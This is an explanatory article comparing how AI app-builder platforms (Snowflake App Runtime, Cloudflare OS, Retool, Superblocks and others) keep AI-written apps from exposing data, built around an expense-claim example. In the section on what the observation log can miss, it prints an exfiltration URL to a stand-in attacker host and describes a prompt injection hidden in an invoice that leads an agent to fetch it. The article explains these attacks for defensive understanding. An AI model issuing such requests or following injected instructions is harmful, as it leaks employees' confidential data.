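A company login keeps strangers out of the expense app, but Ana is an employee, so the faulty handler would still send her Ben's hotel bill. In November 2025, the web hosting company Vercel and the data storage and analysis company Snowflake announced a design meant to prevent this too, for apps made with v0, Vercel's AI app builder. @cramforce wrote in a post about the design that Vercel wanted security that would hold "even if we cannot trust the builder nor the AI". Cloudflare, Retool and Superblocks offer platforms or designs with similar aims. All of them can keep the login out of the generated code, but on each the AI can still write an app that shows Ana the bill unless somebody has set up the right protection.

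### Ana's request to Snowflake

Suppose the company keeps its expense claims in Snowflake, with a row rule that lets employees read only their own. Under the November design, Ana's request for claim 417 would go like this:

1. Vercel's platform makes her log in with her company account before any generated code runs.
2. The platform passes her request to the app, which has no database password and no permission of its own to query anything.
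3. The faulty handler asks for claim 417, and the query reaches Snowflake with Ana's identity attached.
4. Snowflake checks what Ana may read, applies the row rule and returns nothing.

With ordinary row-level security, the app often sends the visitor's identity to the database, so bad code can send someone else's. Here the login layer supplies the identity, so the handler can't identify Ana as Ben.

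Vercel claimed in its announcement that there was "no risk of vibe-coded apps exposing unauthorized data". Customers could only join a waiting list at that point, so the claim had no track record. It also assumes that the customer's permissions in Snowflake are correct. That is plausible for sales figures that have been there for years, but if the office manager's app creates a new table for claims, somebody has to write the row rule first.

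The product changed before customers could use it. In the original plan, the app and its login would run on Vercel's servers. Vercel's *Snowflake*, a guide to the integration, describes a beta in which Snowflake hosts the finished apps instead. The apps now use Snowflake App Runtime, which became generally available on 1 September (Snowflake, 2026). The runtime also handles login, but it gives each app its own permissions, which the November design had ruled out.

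### The same query with different rights

An app on Snowflake App Runtime can query data in two ways. With *owner's rights*, the query uses the permissions of the app's *execution role*, which is normally the role of whoever created the app. With *caller's rights*, it uses the permissions of the person who opened the app. The generated code picks one, using functions that Snowflake provides:

```js
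const sql = "SELECT * FROM claims WHERE id = ?";

// Owner's rights
await snowflake.query(sql, { binds: [417] });

// Caller's rights
const caller = snowflake.asCaller({ headers: request.headers });
await caller.query(sql, { binds: [417] });
```

If the execution role can read the whole table, the first query returns Ben's hotel bill to Ana, but the second returns no row. Snowflake attaches a token that identifies Ana to each of her requests, and `asCaller` uses that token for the second query.

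Snowflake adds a further condition to caller's rights. Snowflake's *Restricted caller’s rights* explains that an app can use one of the caller's permissions only if an administrator has allowed it to, through a *caller grant*. Suppose Ana may read and delete her own claims, while the execution role may read and delete everyone's. The same two commands then have very different effects:

| Mode | `SELECT * FROM claims` | `DELETE FROM claims` |
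|---|---|---|
| Owner's rights | Returns everyone's claims | Deletes everyone's claims |
| Caller's rights without restrictions | Returns Ana's claims | Deletes Ana's claims |
| Restricted, with no caller grant | Fails | Fails |
| Restricted, with a grant to read claims | Returns Ana's claims | Fails |

An administrator creates the grant in the last row with a command such as `GRANT CALLER SELECT ON TABLE claims TO ROLE expense_app`. The grant lets the app use Ana's permission to read claims, if she has one, but gives the app no permission of its own to read them.

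### Owner's rights bring back the missing check

Snowflake App Runtime uses owner's rights unless the code asks for caller's rights. With owner's rights, the database can't distinguish one user from another. If an app's users have different levels of trust, Snowflake instructs developers to "enforce access control in your application logic before returning sensitive data". Its example first runs a small caller's-rights query to check whether the visitor is an analyst. An `if` statement rejects everyone else, and the handler then fetches the data with owner's rights. The query's result is trustworthy, but the `if` statement that acts on it is in the handler, where the AI can leave it out.

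The November promise therefore depends on the AI choosing the right function, and it might choose the wrong one to get rid of an error. A caller's-rights query can't read any claims until an administrator has created the caller grants. If the AI switches to owner's rights, the app starts working and the office manager sees her claims. Deng and colleagues found flaws of this kind in ordinary apps, but the evidence here doesn't show how often they occur on Snowflake.

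An administrator could close this gap by giving the app an execution role that has caller grants but can't read the claims table itself. An owner's-rights query would then fail, and somebody would notice. Snowflake says administrators can't directly limit the permissions of a developer's execution role, but they can control which roles may create apps and in which databases. By default, any user can put an app in a personal database, where it runs under a role the user controls.

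Until July 2026, apps in Snowflake personal databases ran owner's-rights queries with all of the owner's additional roles and couldn't use caller's rights at all, which made them riskier. Snowflake then changed this for new apps, but an older app keeps its broad access until somebody deletes and recreates it.

Some apps need owner's rights, such as one that shows the finance department the quarterly total but not the individual claims. For an app with several audiences, Snowflake suggests either using caller's rights or creating a separate copy for each audience, each copy with its own execution role.

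Other companies' tools offer a similar choice. Databricks, a Snowflake competitor, describes a mode in which everyone who uses an app shares one account's permissions. Apps published with the app builder from Datadog, a monitoring software company, use their author's identity by default. Datadog argues that this improves security because an app can't carry out sensitive operations in the name of whoever opens it.

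### When Maria opens the app

Datadog's concern is reasonable because a caller's-rights app gets some of Maria's permissions when she opens it, and she can read her whole team's claims. Snowflake warns that an app might use a highly privileged visitor's access to copy data, delete tables or give other people permissions. The app's developer doesn't need to have any of those permissions for this to happen.

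Caller grants limit this. They work a little like Java's stack inspection, but compare only two parties. Code with restricted caller's rights also can't grant permissions to others or switch to another role. But it can keep any data it is allowed to read. For example, an app with a grant to read claims can fetch the claims of Maria's entire team and write them to a log that the developer can open.

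An honest mistake can also mix up two visitors, because one running copy of the app serves everybody. Snowflake's guide warns against storing a user's identity in a variable that all requests share. The same mistake with `asCaller` might look like this:

```js
let caller;   // one variable for all visitors

export async function GET(request) {
  caller = snowflake.asCaller({ headers: request.headers });
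  const id = await findClaimId(request);
  const { rows } = await caller.query(
    "SELECT * FROM claims WHERE id = ?", { binds: [id] });
  return Response.json(rows);
}
```

If Ben opens the app while Ana's request is waiting for `findClaimId`, his request overwrites `caller`, and Ana's query then runs with his permissions. She gets his hotel bill even though the AI chose caller's rights and the row rule is correct. @cramforce's claim that users never see unauthorised data "even if the app has bugs" is therefore too strong for this runtime. A platform that runs a separate copy of the app for each person would not have this problem.

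### Cloudflare's named connections

Cloudflare's design guide, quoted at the start of this reference, is for companies that want to build their own vibe-coding platform. It explains how to combine Cloudflare's products and contains no test results. Ana's request first reaches Access, Cloudflare's login proxy, which checks whether she may use the expense app. The request then goes to a *dispatch worker*, a program written by the platform's operators. The dispatch worker can apply finer rules based on her role, and it limits how long the app may run and how many requests it may send. The generated code starts only after these steps.

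The generated code reaches data through *bindings*, which are named connections that the platform attaches to an app. The expense app might have one called `CLAIMS_DB`. The code uses the name and never handles an address or a password, and it can't use a binding that the platform hasn't attached. A binding is close to Hardy's idea of a capability. Cloudflare suggests giving each app its own database and storage if the company wants complete isolation.

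This keeps the expense app out of the payroll database, whatever the AI writes. But it doesn't protect Ben from Ana, because `CLAIMS_DB` opens the same database for every visitor. Protecting him would take a narrower binding, like the `myClaims` object in the earlier example.

Vercel's newer login product, Passport, has the same limit when a company uses it alone. Vercel says that Passport, like Google's proxy, gives the app a signed identity header. The app's server code still has to handle authorization, according to Vercel's *Read Passport identity in your application*. Grosser says in *Vercel for Enterprise* that a companion product, Connect, carries each employee's permissions through to the data source. That would be a form of caller's rights, and it would protect Ben if the source had a correct rule for claims.

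### A key that the code can use but not read

Apps often need a secret key for an outside service, such as the company's payroll provider. Generated code can leak a key that is stored in the code itself or in a file beside it. Snowflake's runtime has this weakness because the code can read the app's own access token. The runtime replaces the token regularly, but Snowflake still has to warn developers not to log it.

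Cloudflare keeps such keys outside the sandbox. Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026) describes a proxy that intercepts the app's outgoing requests and adds the key on the way. The platform's operators write its rules in JavaScript. A rule for the payroll provider, adapted from Cloudflare's examples, might be:

```js
ExpenseSandbox.outboundByHost = {
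  "payroll.example": (request, env) => {
    if (request.method !== "GET")
      return new Response("Not allowed", { status: 405 });

    const withKey = new Request(request);
    withKey.headers.set("x-auth-token", env.PAYROLL_KEY);
    return fetch(withKey);
  },
};
```

The app sends an ordinary request to `payroll.example` without a key. The proxy rejects anything except a GET request, the type that normally only reads data. It copies the GET request, adds the key and sends the copy to the provider.

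The proxy has to decrypt requests to do this. For each sandbox, Cloudflare creates a temporary *certificate authority*, which certifies the identity of websites. The sandbox trusts this authority, so the proxy can stand in for the payroll provider and decrypt the request. The authority's private key stays in a process outside the sandbox.

This arrangement prevents theft of the key. The AI can't print it on a page, and an attacker who takes over the app can't copy it and use it later from another computer. The company can also replace the key without changing the app.

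Having the proxy add the key does not by itself prevent misuse. The proxy will add the key to any request it lets through from the generated code, which makes it a potential confused deputy. Without the GET condition in the example, a faulty or malicious app could pay Ana's hotel bill ten times. The protection comes from the conditions someone writes into the proxy and any limits the payroll provider places on the key.

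Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes several such conditions. The proxy can restrict which sites an app may contact and what it may do there. It can also record each request and change the rules while the app runs. For example, it might allow downloads while the app installs packages and then block all web traffic. Once operators set a list of allowed sites, the proxy blocks all others, following the principle of fail-safe defaults.

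The GET rule still wouldn't stop the app from fetching Ben's bank details for Ana. In Cloudflare's examples, the proxy identifies the sandbox that sent a request, not the person using the app. If each employee has a separate sandbox, the proxy can tell them apart and use a different key for each sandbox or restrict each one to its own folder in shared storage. If all employees share one sandbox, the app has to check who is making the request, or the proxy needs another reliable way to identify that person.

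Data can also leak through an allowed site. If the app is allowed to post to GitHub, it could put the company's claims in a public project there, so the operators would also have to restrict which projects it can write to.

### Retool's rules on the data connection

Retool has long sold software for building internal tools. It now lets an AI write them and also hosts apps from other AI builders. When it launched this version, Retool said that every app inherits login, roles and data access policies and that "none of it lives in the app code". Its description of the product is consistent with this for login and database passwords. An administrator sets up each data connection, and according to Retool, the generated code uses short-lived tokens to reach the data through Retool without exposing the password.

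Whether data permissions stay out of the AI-written code depends on a setting. The older method puts the visitor's identity in each query, for example `WHERE owner_id = {{current_user.id}}`. Retool fills in the value on its server, and an optional check rejects any attempt by the visitor to change it. But Retool's *Restrict access with the current_user object* states that a query without the filter returns everything, which is the flaw in the claim 417 handler.

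The newer method puts the rule on the connection. Retool's *Access policies* describes rules for which tables, columns and rows each group may reach, and Retool applies them to every query through the connection. They would protect Ben even if the AI left out the filter. According to Retool's *Access policies for PostgreSQL resources in public beta*, they are available to Enterprise customers and only for PostgreSQL databases.

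Once these rules are on, the connection is closed to everyone by default, and Retool blocks any query it can't fully analyse, according to its *Data access enforcement*. It also rejects queries that use a forbidden column only as a search condition, since a search can reveal a hidden value. Scheduled jobs fail because Retool can't determine whose permissions to apply.

But enforcement is off by default, and the owner of a connection can switch it off again. Retool's row rules check which existing rows Ana may read or change, but not what she writes. Ana couldn't read claim 417, but she could file a new claim in Ben's name or make him the owner of one of hers. PostgreSQL's own row-level security can prevent this, and Retool recommends adding a constraint in the database to stop it.

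### Superblocks leaves the check to its AI

Superblocks, another builder of internal tools, supplies a reliable identity and lets its AI agent, Clark, write the authorization. Every backend function receives `ctx.user`, which comes from the login session and can't be changed by visitors. Superblocks tells builders to describe who should see what, and Clark adds the matching checks and filters to the code. This is better than trusting an email address sent by the browser, but every backend function still needs its own filter, and the office manager has to remember to tell Clark that claims are private.

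The permissions on a data connection don't help Ben either, because they only limit who can build with it. Superblocks says that people who use a published app need no access to the connection, and that this is intentional. The effect is similar to owner's rights.

Companies can choose a stricter arrangement for some data sources. For example, Superblocks can use the login service Okta to connect to Snowflake on behalf of the current user, so that Snowflake applies that user's permissions. In its marketing, Superblocks warns that without this arrangement, "the app enforces your permissions model on screen while bypassing it underneath" (*Prototypes Are the Tip of the Iceberg*, 2026).

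### Run-time controls and checks before release

These companies often advertise two kinds of protection together. Run-time controls apply to each request, including requests that nobody foresaw. Checks before release look for mistakes in the code and can miss some. For claim 417, the four platforms compare as follows:

| Platform | What could stop Ana at run time | Who has to set it up | Checks before release |
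|---|---|---|---|
| Snowflake App Runtime | Her own Snowflake permissions | An administrator, and the AI by choosing caller's rights | Developers' own checks of their code and packages |
| Cloudflare's design | A check in the app, or separate data for each person | The AI or the platform's operators | Scans, and human review where required |
| Retool | An access policy on the connection | The connection's owner | Code analysis and approval of some actions |
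| Superblocks | A filter in the app, or the data source's own permissions | The AI or an administrator | Scanners and AI security agents |

Retool checks the code its agent writes before anyone can save or run it. Retool's *App security* says the platform rejects code that uses a data connection the builder isn't allowed to edit. This restricts the office manager while she builds the app, but it doesn't affect which claims Ana can read later. Retool also looks for code that puts a visitor's text directly into a database command. It refuses public software packages less than five days old, since people often discover malicious ones quickly.

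According to Retool's marketing, a person must review any change to production data before the agent makes it. But according to its documentation, builders on the cloud version can turn these approvals off unless an administrator prevents it. Builders who get tired of approving changes may well do so.

Superblocks goes further in trying to find missing authorization. *Superblocks 3.0* (Menezes, 2026) describes AI agents that check every change before release for ways around an app's permissions. Menezes, the company's chief executive, gives no figures for how many flaws the agents find or miss. The agents might detect that one handler lacks a filter that all the others have. If no handler has the filter, they would need some other indication that claims are private.

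Vercel said in 2025 that v0 had blocked more than 17,000 deployments in 30 days because they would have exposed secrets. Over a thousand people had been about to publish keys to their Supabase databases or backends. These are Vercel's own counts, and they don't show how many exposed secrets v0 missed. Keys are easier to recognise than a missing ownership check, because many have a fixed format. If the platform adds keys outside the sandbox, as Cloudflare's proxy does, the generated code doesn't contain those keys and can't expose them.

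## August 2026: Cloudflare OS and apps that start with no access

On Snowflake, Retool and Superblocks, many people use the same copy of an app, so something has to work out whose data each person may see. Cloudflare took a different approach in August 2026 with Cloudflare OS, an open-source platform on which an AI agent writes small apps for employees. Each document gets its own copy of the app, and a new app can reach only its own database until somebody connects it to something else.

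Varda designed the platform as a remake of Sandstorm. In a launch post quoted in *an agent workspace built on cloudflare workers*, a forum page about the project, he wrote that on this platform "the AI cannot introduce a significant security bug". That is true of the faulty handler for claim 417 if each claim has its own copy of the app, but not if the office manager shares one copy with the whole company. The platform also doesn't catch a few other serious mistakes the AI can make, such as writing salaries into code that somebody then passes on.

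Cloudflare gave all its employees a first version of Cloudflare OS in May 2026. Jones and Carter report in the launch announcement, *Cloudflare OS*, that thousands of them use it every day. The apps in that version were static, and people worked in private. When they began to share their work, Cloudflare knew which tools an agent could call but not which records the agent had read, so the company couldn't tell who should see the results. Cloudflare rebuilt the platform to solve this, so much of its internal experience is with the older design.

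AgentPedia's *Cloudflare OS*, an independent guide, reports that by Cloudflare's own count, employees had built over 4,000 apps or tools and the sales teams had saved over 10,000 hours in one 30-day period. These figures measure use rather than security, but with so many apps, nobody is likely to review each one by hand. Cloudflare also admits that giving coding tools to everyone produced "a flood of vibe coded apps looking for a problem to solve".

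### One gadget for each claim

A *gadget* is one copy of an app together with its data. The agent writes two programs for it, one that draws the page in the user's browser and one that runs on the server and stores the data. The server program is a *Dynamic Worker*, which the platform loads into a V8 isolate when somebody needs it, so no document needs an idle container. The worker has its own SQLite database, separate from the software that manages it.

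The generated code has no part in deciding who can enter Cloudflare OS or use a gadget. Cloudflare's login proxy controls entry, and each gadget is private until its owner shares it through a dialog like the one in Google Docs.

If each expense claim is a gadget, the faulty handler can't show Ben's hotel bill to Ana, for the same reasons as on Sandstorm. Her gadget's database holds only claim 416, and the platform won't let her open Ben's gadget.

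This design also makes it less harmful for a gadget to mix up two visitors, as happened with the shared `caller` variable on Snowflake, because everyone who can open a gadget is allowed to see all the data in it.

That last condition is easy to break. People can share their work on Cloudflare OS in two ways. They can share the gadget itself, or they can share a *blueprint*, which contains the app's code but not its data. The office manager's choice between the two decides whether Ben's hotel bill is safe:

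| What the office manager shares | What each employee gets | Can Ana read claim 417? |
|---|---|---|
| One gadget for all claims | The same app and the same database | Yes, if the handler lacks the ownership check |
| A blueprint | A new gadget with an empty database | No, unless Ben shares his gadget with her |

The first option, a shared gadget, brings back the original flaw in full. Varda argues that the platform can manage all access control by controlling who can open a gadget, but the platform has no rule for who may see which part of a gadget. The office manager may well choose the shared gadget anyway, because it gives the finance department its quarterly total with no extra work. With blueprints, somebody has to collect the claims from every employee's separate database.

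Separate copies also let people change their apps without affecting anyone else. When Varda asked Claude to make a slide deck, Claude found that the editor couldn't strike through or centre text, and added both features. If it had broken something, the damage would have been limited to that deck.

This freedom is a problem for an expense claim. Ana owns the gadget for claim 416, so she could ask the agent to change the gadget's code so that the page shows the claim as approved by Maria, without breaking out of any sandbox. The company would have to keep its approvals somewhere that Ana can't edit.

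### A malicious script in claim 416

The drawing feature that Claude added to Varda's slide editor may have been vulnerable to *cross-site scripting*, in which an attacker gets a page to run their script in someone else's browser. On an ordinary website, such a script can often use the victim's login and send whatever it finds to the attacker.

Suppose the AI makes the same mistake in the expense app. Ana hides a script in the description of claim 416 and shares the gadget with Maria. When Maria opens the claim, her browser runs the script.

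The page runs in an *iframe*, a web page embedded in another page. According to the write-up of Varda's talk, this frame has a "null origin", so the browser treats it as belonging to no website and denies it access to cookies. A *Content Security Policy*, a list of what a page may load and contact, blocks communication with the outside. The script can still send messages to the surrounding Cloudflare OS page, which passes them to the gadget's own server program.

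That server program has no network access either. Simplified, the platform loads it with settings like these:

```js
{
  mainModule: "server.js",
  modules: { "server.js": generatedCode },
  env: { TRAVEL: travelBookings },   // the only outside resource
  globalOutbound: null               // no other network access
}
```

The last setting makes every attempt to open a network connection fail. If the platform's developers forgot it, the generated code would inherit the network access of the program that loaded it. Inheriting access by default goes against the principle of fail-safe defaults, but the developers have to set this correctly only once for all gadgets.

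The script in claim 416 could therefore do some things and not others:

| What the script tries when Maria opens the claim | Result |
|---|---|
| Read Maria's login cookie | Fails, because the frame belongs to no website |
| Send the claim to a server on the internet | Fails, because of the Content Security Policy |
| Read Ben's claim, which Maria may open | Fails, because this gadget has no connection to that one |
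| Change the amount or delete a receipt | Works, because the app itself can do this |
| Press the app's "Approve" button | Works, if the app has one |
| Ask for Maria's password and save it in the gadget's database | Works if she types it, and Ana can then read it |

The last three results follow from the design, because the script can do whatever the page can do. Ana gains nothing by deleting a receipt, since the claim is hers. The platform keeps the damage inside one gadget, which is much better than an ordinary website would do, but a false approval in Maria's name could still be worth a lot of money, and most companies would call it a significant security bug.

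All of this assumes that the isolation holds. Neither Varda's talk nor the launch announcement reports an outside test like the one DEVCORE carried out on Sandstorm. The developers of *workerd*, the open-source program that runs Workers, also warn that it is not a hardened sandbox by itself. Cloudflare's hosting adds further layers of protection, but a company that runs Cloudflare OS on its own servers has to add them itself, for example by putting the whole system in a virtual machine.

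### Gatekeepers and narrow connections

Most useful apps need data from elsewhere. Jones and Carter observe that people who start experimenting with AI at work often ask for API keys, the secret codes that let a program use a company system. These keys usually give broad access and stay valid for a long time.

On Cloudflare OS, an agent asks for one specific resource and the user grants or refuses it. If the expense app has permission to see Ana's travel bookings, its code might contain:

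```js
const trips = await env.TRAVEL.listTrips({
  traveller: "ana",
  month: "2026-08",
});
```

`env.TRAVEL` is a capability for those bookings. Requests made through it go to a *Gatekeeper*, a program written for one outside service. The Gatekeeper logs in to the travel system, holds the credential and carries out the request. Neither the agent nor the generated code has access to the credential.

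A Gatekeeper can be much more selective than a key. For GitHub, it could give an agent access to a single repository and let it read reported issues but not source code. It could also blank out particular fields, limit the number of requests, and require a person's approval before the agent merges a change.

Cloudflare's credential proxy, which adds keys to outgoing requests, can apply some of the same limits. But it works on web requests, so someone has to write "may read Ana's bookings" as a rule about addresses and request types. A Gatekeeper's author knows what each of the service's operations does and can provide an operation for this purpose. If `env.TRAVEL` covers only Ana's bookings, the AI gets nothing when it changes the traveller to Ben.

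The office manager might connect everyone's bookings by mistake. Varda says that when somebody shares a gadget, the platform checks that each recipient has direct permission to use every resource connected to it. Ana has no permission for the full set of bookings, so she couldn't open the gadget. The owner's-rights apps on Snowflake have no such check.

Many companies already connect their AI tools through a common standard, the Model Context Protocol (MCP). An MCP server can also hold the credential and offer a fixed set of tools. Cloudflare OS supports these servers but has less information about what the agent reads through them. According to *Data Read by Agents*, an outside developer's study of the source code, users therefore can't share a generic MCP connection. They have to share a blueprint instead, and each recipient connects their own account.

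### Twenty-five actions waiting for approval

Once a user attaches a resource, the agent can read it without asking again. Actions with external effects, such as sending an email, can require a person's approval.

Frequent requests for approval cause *approval fatigue*, in which people get so used to approving requests that they stop reading them. Some turn on automatic approval to stop the interruptions. In Varda's remedy, the Gatekeeper holds back each action and simulates the result so that the agent can keep working with it. The user approves or rejects the whole batch at the end.

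Suppose the office manager asks for help with late expense claims. The agent creates a shared folder, puts twelve reports in it and drafts an email to each employee with a link. None of these actions has taken effect yet. The Gatekeeper gave the agent a simulated folder so that the agent could prepare all 25 actions without stopping.

AgentPedia asks what happens if the user rejects an early action that later ones depend on. If the manager refuses the folder but approves the emails, twelve people could get a broken link. A Gatekeeper's author therefore has to simulate the service accurately and track dependencies between actions, which is much more work than passing requests along.

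Batching reduces interruptions but not the number of decisions. A manager may read a list of 25 actions more carefully than 25 separate pop-ups, since she can see the whole plan. She may also glance at the first three and approve everything, including any harmful email near the end. Varda says only that he hopes people will no longer feel the need for automatic approval, which they can still switch on, and he gives no figures on how often users reject anything.

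Varda also pointed out at the launch that a gadget gets only the access a user explicitly grants it. One critic replied that this is also true of phishing websites, where people give things away by agreeing to something they haven't understood. Explicit grants limit the damage from a careless decision without making people more careful.

A better defence is to ask only when it matters. The platform can use its record of what the agent has read to flag dangerous actions. For example, an email to Ben about his own claim may need little attention, but it deserves a warning if the agent has just read the payroll. Varda said this part of the system was still evolving.

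### Sharing a payroll dashboard

That record is the *observation log*, and it addresses the problem Cloudflare had with its first version. *Data Read by Agents* illustrates the problem with a payroll dashboard. Suppose Clara, who runs human resources, asks an agent for a dashboard of average salaries by team, and the agent makes it from the payroll database. Clara then sends Maria, who isn't allowed to see payroll data, a link to the *workspace*, which holds the conversation, the files and the dashboard.

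An ordinary permission check would not help, because it runs when the agent reads the database for Clara, who has access. By the time Maria clicks the link, the salaries are already in a finished chart.

On Cloudflare OS, the Gatekeeper for the payroll database has to report each read by calling `authorizeObservation()`. The platform stores the identity of the source and the permission needed to read it. When Maria tries to open the workspace, the platform checks each stored source again, using her permissions. She fails the check for payroll, so she can't open the workspace.

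If Maria had joined the workspace before Clara asked for salaries, the platform would have blocked the agent from reading the payroll database at all. Both checks enforce one rule. Let *O* be the set of sources that the agent has read in a workspace, and *R(u)* the set of sources that person *u* may read. The platform tries to ensure that

*O* ⊆ *R(u)* for every person *u* who can open the workspace.

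A new person can join only if they are allowed to read everything in *O*. The agent can read a new source only if everyone who has already joined is allowed to read it.

Some sources are so sensitive that only the workspace's owner may see them. After the agent reads one of these, the platform locks the workspace. Clara can't invite anyone else, and the agent loses its tools for retrieving public web pages. Varda says a Gatekeeper can also forbid the agent to write anywhere else after such a read. He says this allowed Cloudflare to connect the system to its own customer data and revenue figures.

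This is a coarse form of information flow control, with one label for the whole workspace. The platform doesn't examine the dashboard, so the protection doesn't depend on how the AI wrote it. Even an indirect leak, such as a chart that turns red when a salary passes a limit, goes through the same check. The generated code can't remove the label, because the platform keeps the log outside the gadget.

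The drawback is a lot of over-labelling. If Clara's agent also makes a chart of how many people work in each team, Maria can't open it in this workspace, though it contains nothing secret. Clara would have to remake it in a new workspace. The average salaries may also be harmless for large teams, but the checks described in *Data Read by Agents* have no exception for harmless summaries. *Data Read by Agents* suggests tracking individual files when several departments work together. Varda called the current policies "a bit blunt right now, maybe overly restrictive" and expected to refine them.

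### What the log can miss

The log is complete only if Gatekeepers report every read, and *Data Read by Agents* warns that the platform's core can't force them to. A Gatekeeper might report the first page of a long list and omit the later ones, or answer from a stored copy without reporting anything. The platform would then let Maria in, because the log would contain no reason to keep her out.

Every Gatekeeper is therefore part of the trusted computing base. Varda reports that AI can write Gatekeepers quickly for almost any service, so some of this trusted code is AI-written too.

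A Gatekeeper can also record every read but in too little detail. Suppose the company keeps its expense claims in a database table with a row rule, and Maria's agent makes a report on her team's claims. If the Gatekeeper records only that the agent read the claims table, Ana passes the check, because she is also allowed to query that table. She can then see Ben's hotel bill in Maria's report, even though the row rule would have shown her only claim 416. To prevent this, the Gatekeeper would have to record which rows the agent read.

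The log also covers only data that came through a Gatekeeper. If Ben types his hotel bill into an expense gadget that the whole company shares, the log doesn't protect him because there is no outside source to check. The platform can verify who may see the company's payroll database because the database already has permissions, but no one has set permissions for a form that the AI wrote this morning.

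Jones and Carter explain that reading sensitive data can prevent an agent from writing to certain places, inviting collaborators, handing work to another agent or making outside requests. *Data Read by Agents* found no single check that covers every route by which data can leave. Retrieving a web page, calling an AI model and publishing a blueprint each had separate controls. The author read the code shortly after its release, while the project was changing quickly, so later versions may differ.

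Retrieving a page looks like reading, but a request can carry data out in the address itself:

```
https://attacker.example/?salary=58000
```

An attacker could try to trigger such a request through *prompt injection*, which means hiding instructions for the AI in text that it reads. A line in a supplier's invoice might tell the agent to look up an address with a salary filled in. Varda maintains that an agent essentially cannot leak a secret unless the user approves a later write. That can only be true if the platform also controls every tool that only seems to read. Locking the workspace prevents such a leak, but only after reads that a Gatekeeper has marked as very sensitive.

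Calls to an AI model are a different case, because the model has to receive the data to work on it. Varda says the design assumes users trust their model provider. Many providers offer not to keep the data, and a company that trusts none of them can run a model on its own machines.

Another limit is that the platform can control exports but not who opens the exported files. People can, for example, save a presentation as an ordinary file or send it to a service such as Google Drive.

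### Salaries in a blueprint

Blueprints leave out the gadget's database, the conversation with the agent, the credentials and the connected resources. The recipient starts with an empty app and has to connect resources to it. A malicious blueprint therefore can't read anything until its new user grants it access. Varda hopes people will exchange blueprints without worrying about security bugs in them.

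The separation between code and data depends on the AI putting the data in the right place. Suppose the payroll dashboard loads slowly, and Clara asks the agent to make it faster. The agent could copy the figures into the program:

```js
const salaries = {
  ana: 52000,
  ben: 58000,
};
```

The dashboard now opens immediately, and Clara would notice no other difference. Another manager asks for a dashboard like hers, so she shares the blueprint. She assumes it contains no data, and the platform has left out the database. But the salaries are in the code, so everyone who receives the blueprint can read them.

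According to *Data Read by Agents*, the platform doesn't compare the observation log with the recipient's permissions when somebody exports a blueprint. That comparison might have caught the problem, since the log includes the payroll read.

When a reader raised this at the launch, Varda agreed that an agent could put sensitive information in the code, though not API keys, which it never sees. He suggested restricting exports from workspaces that have read secrets, but added that this "might be more annoying than useful".

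I think this is the clearest counterexample to his claim. The AI makes an ordinary programming mistake, the user acts reasonably, every part of the sandbox works, and people still see salaries they have no right to see. Cloudflare could fix this by holding blueprint recipients to its existing rule for opening a workspace. That would stop Clara from sharing some harmless blueprints, and people would probably complain.

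### Tied to one runtime

When Cloudflare OS launched, several programmers objected that it would make companies dependent on Cloudflare. Every gadget and Gatekeeper is a Worker, and the apps use storage and communication systems that Cloudflare designed. The platform initially accepted only JavaScript, so unlike Sandstorm, it could not run existing programs such as Etherpad.

Varda replied that, after his experience with Sandstorm's containers, he could not have built it any other way. He gave up compatibility to get lightweight isolation. The loss of compatibility matters less now than it did in 2014, because an AI can write a new app to suit the platform.

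He also pointed out that the whole system is open source and runs without a Cloudflare account, as it does on a server in his basement. Leaving Cloudflare would be harder for a company. Varda acknowledged at the launch that the part of workerd that stores each gadget's data did not yet scale well across several machines, so the system would work comfortably for one person but might not work well for a whole company. He was working on a fix. AgentPedia notes that the project had not yet published instructions for running it in production outside Cloudflare, and advises companies to stay on a fixed version because the software changes often.

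Its guide also recommends testing the refusals before connecting anything important. A company could share a gadget with somebody who lacks access to the gadget's data, withdraw the owner's own access, and reject a queued action, checking how the platform responds each time. An office manager is unlikely to run these tests, but her company's security team could run them once for everyone.

On 1 October 2026, Cloudflare (2026) opened a waiting list for a version that it will manage itself and that customers can start in a few clicks. Companies that use it should have less to configure and less to get wrong. But they would rely on Cloudflare for the login, the isolation and the observation log, so a single fault at Cloudflare could affect many of them.

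## 2025–2026: Failures in the platforms themselves

A mistake in the platform can expose every app that runs on it, even if each app has perfect access rules, whereas a mistake in the expense app exposes only one company's claims. Between July 2025 and October 2026, researchers found such platform flaws in a login service, in disks that customers shared and in a service that runs AI models. The companies repaired most of them within days, and hundreds of separate app owners could hardly have done so as quickly.

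### Strangers in Base44's private apps

Base44, Wix's app builder, handles the login for the apps its customers make. Owners could make their apps private, and some companies also required employees to use the company login. In July 2025, Wiz reported that outsiders could register for private apps. Base44's registration service required an app's identifier, which wasn't secret, and didn't check whether the app accepted new users.

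Strangers could have gotten into an office manager's app even if she had made it private and confirmed that a logged-out browser showed the login page.

The app's other protections determined what a stranger could read next. A row rule that admits anyone who has logged in would let a stranger read every claim, while a rule that compares each claim's owner with the current user would block them, because a stranger owns no claims.

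Wix fixed the flaw within 24 hours of Wiz's report, and customers did not have to change their apps. Wix found no sign that anyone had exploited it. Imperva, another security company, reported further weaknesses in Base44, some of which could let an attacker take over a user's account.

### Leftover data on Cloudflare's disks

In September 2026, Cloudflare (2026) disclosed a flaw in Containers, its service for running customers' Linux programs. A new container could read data that another customer's deleted container had left on the same server. The flaw also affected Sandboxes, a Containers-based product for running untrusted code, including code from AI agents.

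A storage setting caused the flaw, according to The Hacker News' *Cloudflare Fixes Flaw That Let One Container Read Another Customer's Leftover Disk* (2026). Containers get their disk space in blocks of 64 kilobytes. When a customer deletes a container, its blocks return to a pool that all customers on the server share. Linux normally wipes a block before giving it to the next container, but Cloudflare's setting skipped this step. If the next container filled only part of a block, the rest still held the old data.

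Researchers at the security company Accomplish found leftover data in 18 of 24 attempts, and on 20 of the 22 machines they reached across four continents. The leftovers included complete SQLite databases and files of credentials. An attacker could not choose whose data they got, and the researchers did not show that anyone could change another customer's live data. If the expense app had run in a container and kept its database there, a stranger could have received the whole claims table, including Ben's hotel bill. Rules about who may query the table would not have prevented this, because the stranger would have had the database file itself.

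A week before Accomplish reported the flaw, Cloudflare's documentation stated that sandboxes could not access each other's files because each ran in its own virtual machine. The virtual machines did separate running programs, but the storage under them was shared and had its own settings that also had to be correct.

Another Cloudflare design, the credential proxy, would have limited the damage. It adds secret keys to requests after they leave the sandbox, so an app that uses it does not need to keep those keys on its disk.

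Cloudflare first turned the wiping back on, and on 14 September the researchers confirmed that their method no longer worked. But old data remained on the disks of running containers and in each server's store of prepared software, where new containers could inherit it. Cloudflare therefore replaced every running disk, cleared the stores and restarted servers during quiet hours. It finished on 19 September, 15 days after the report.

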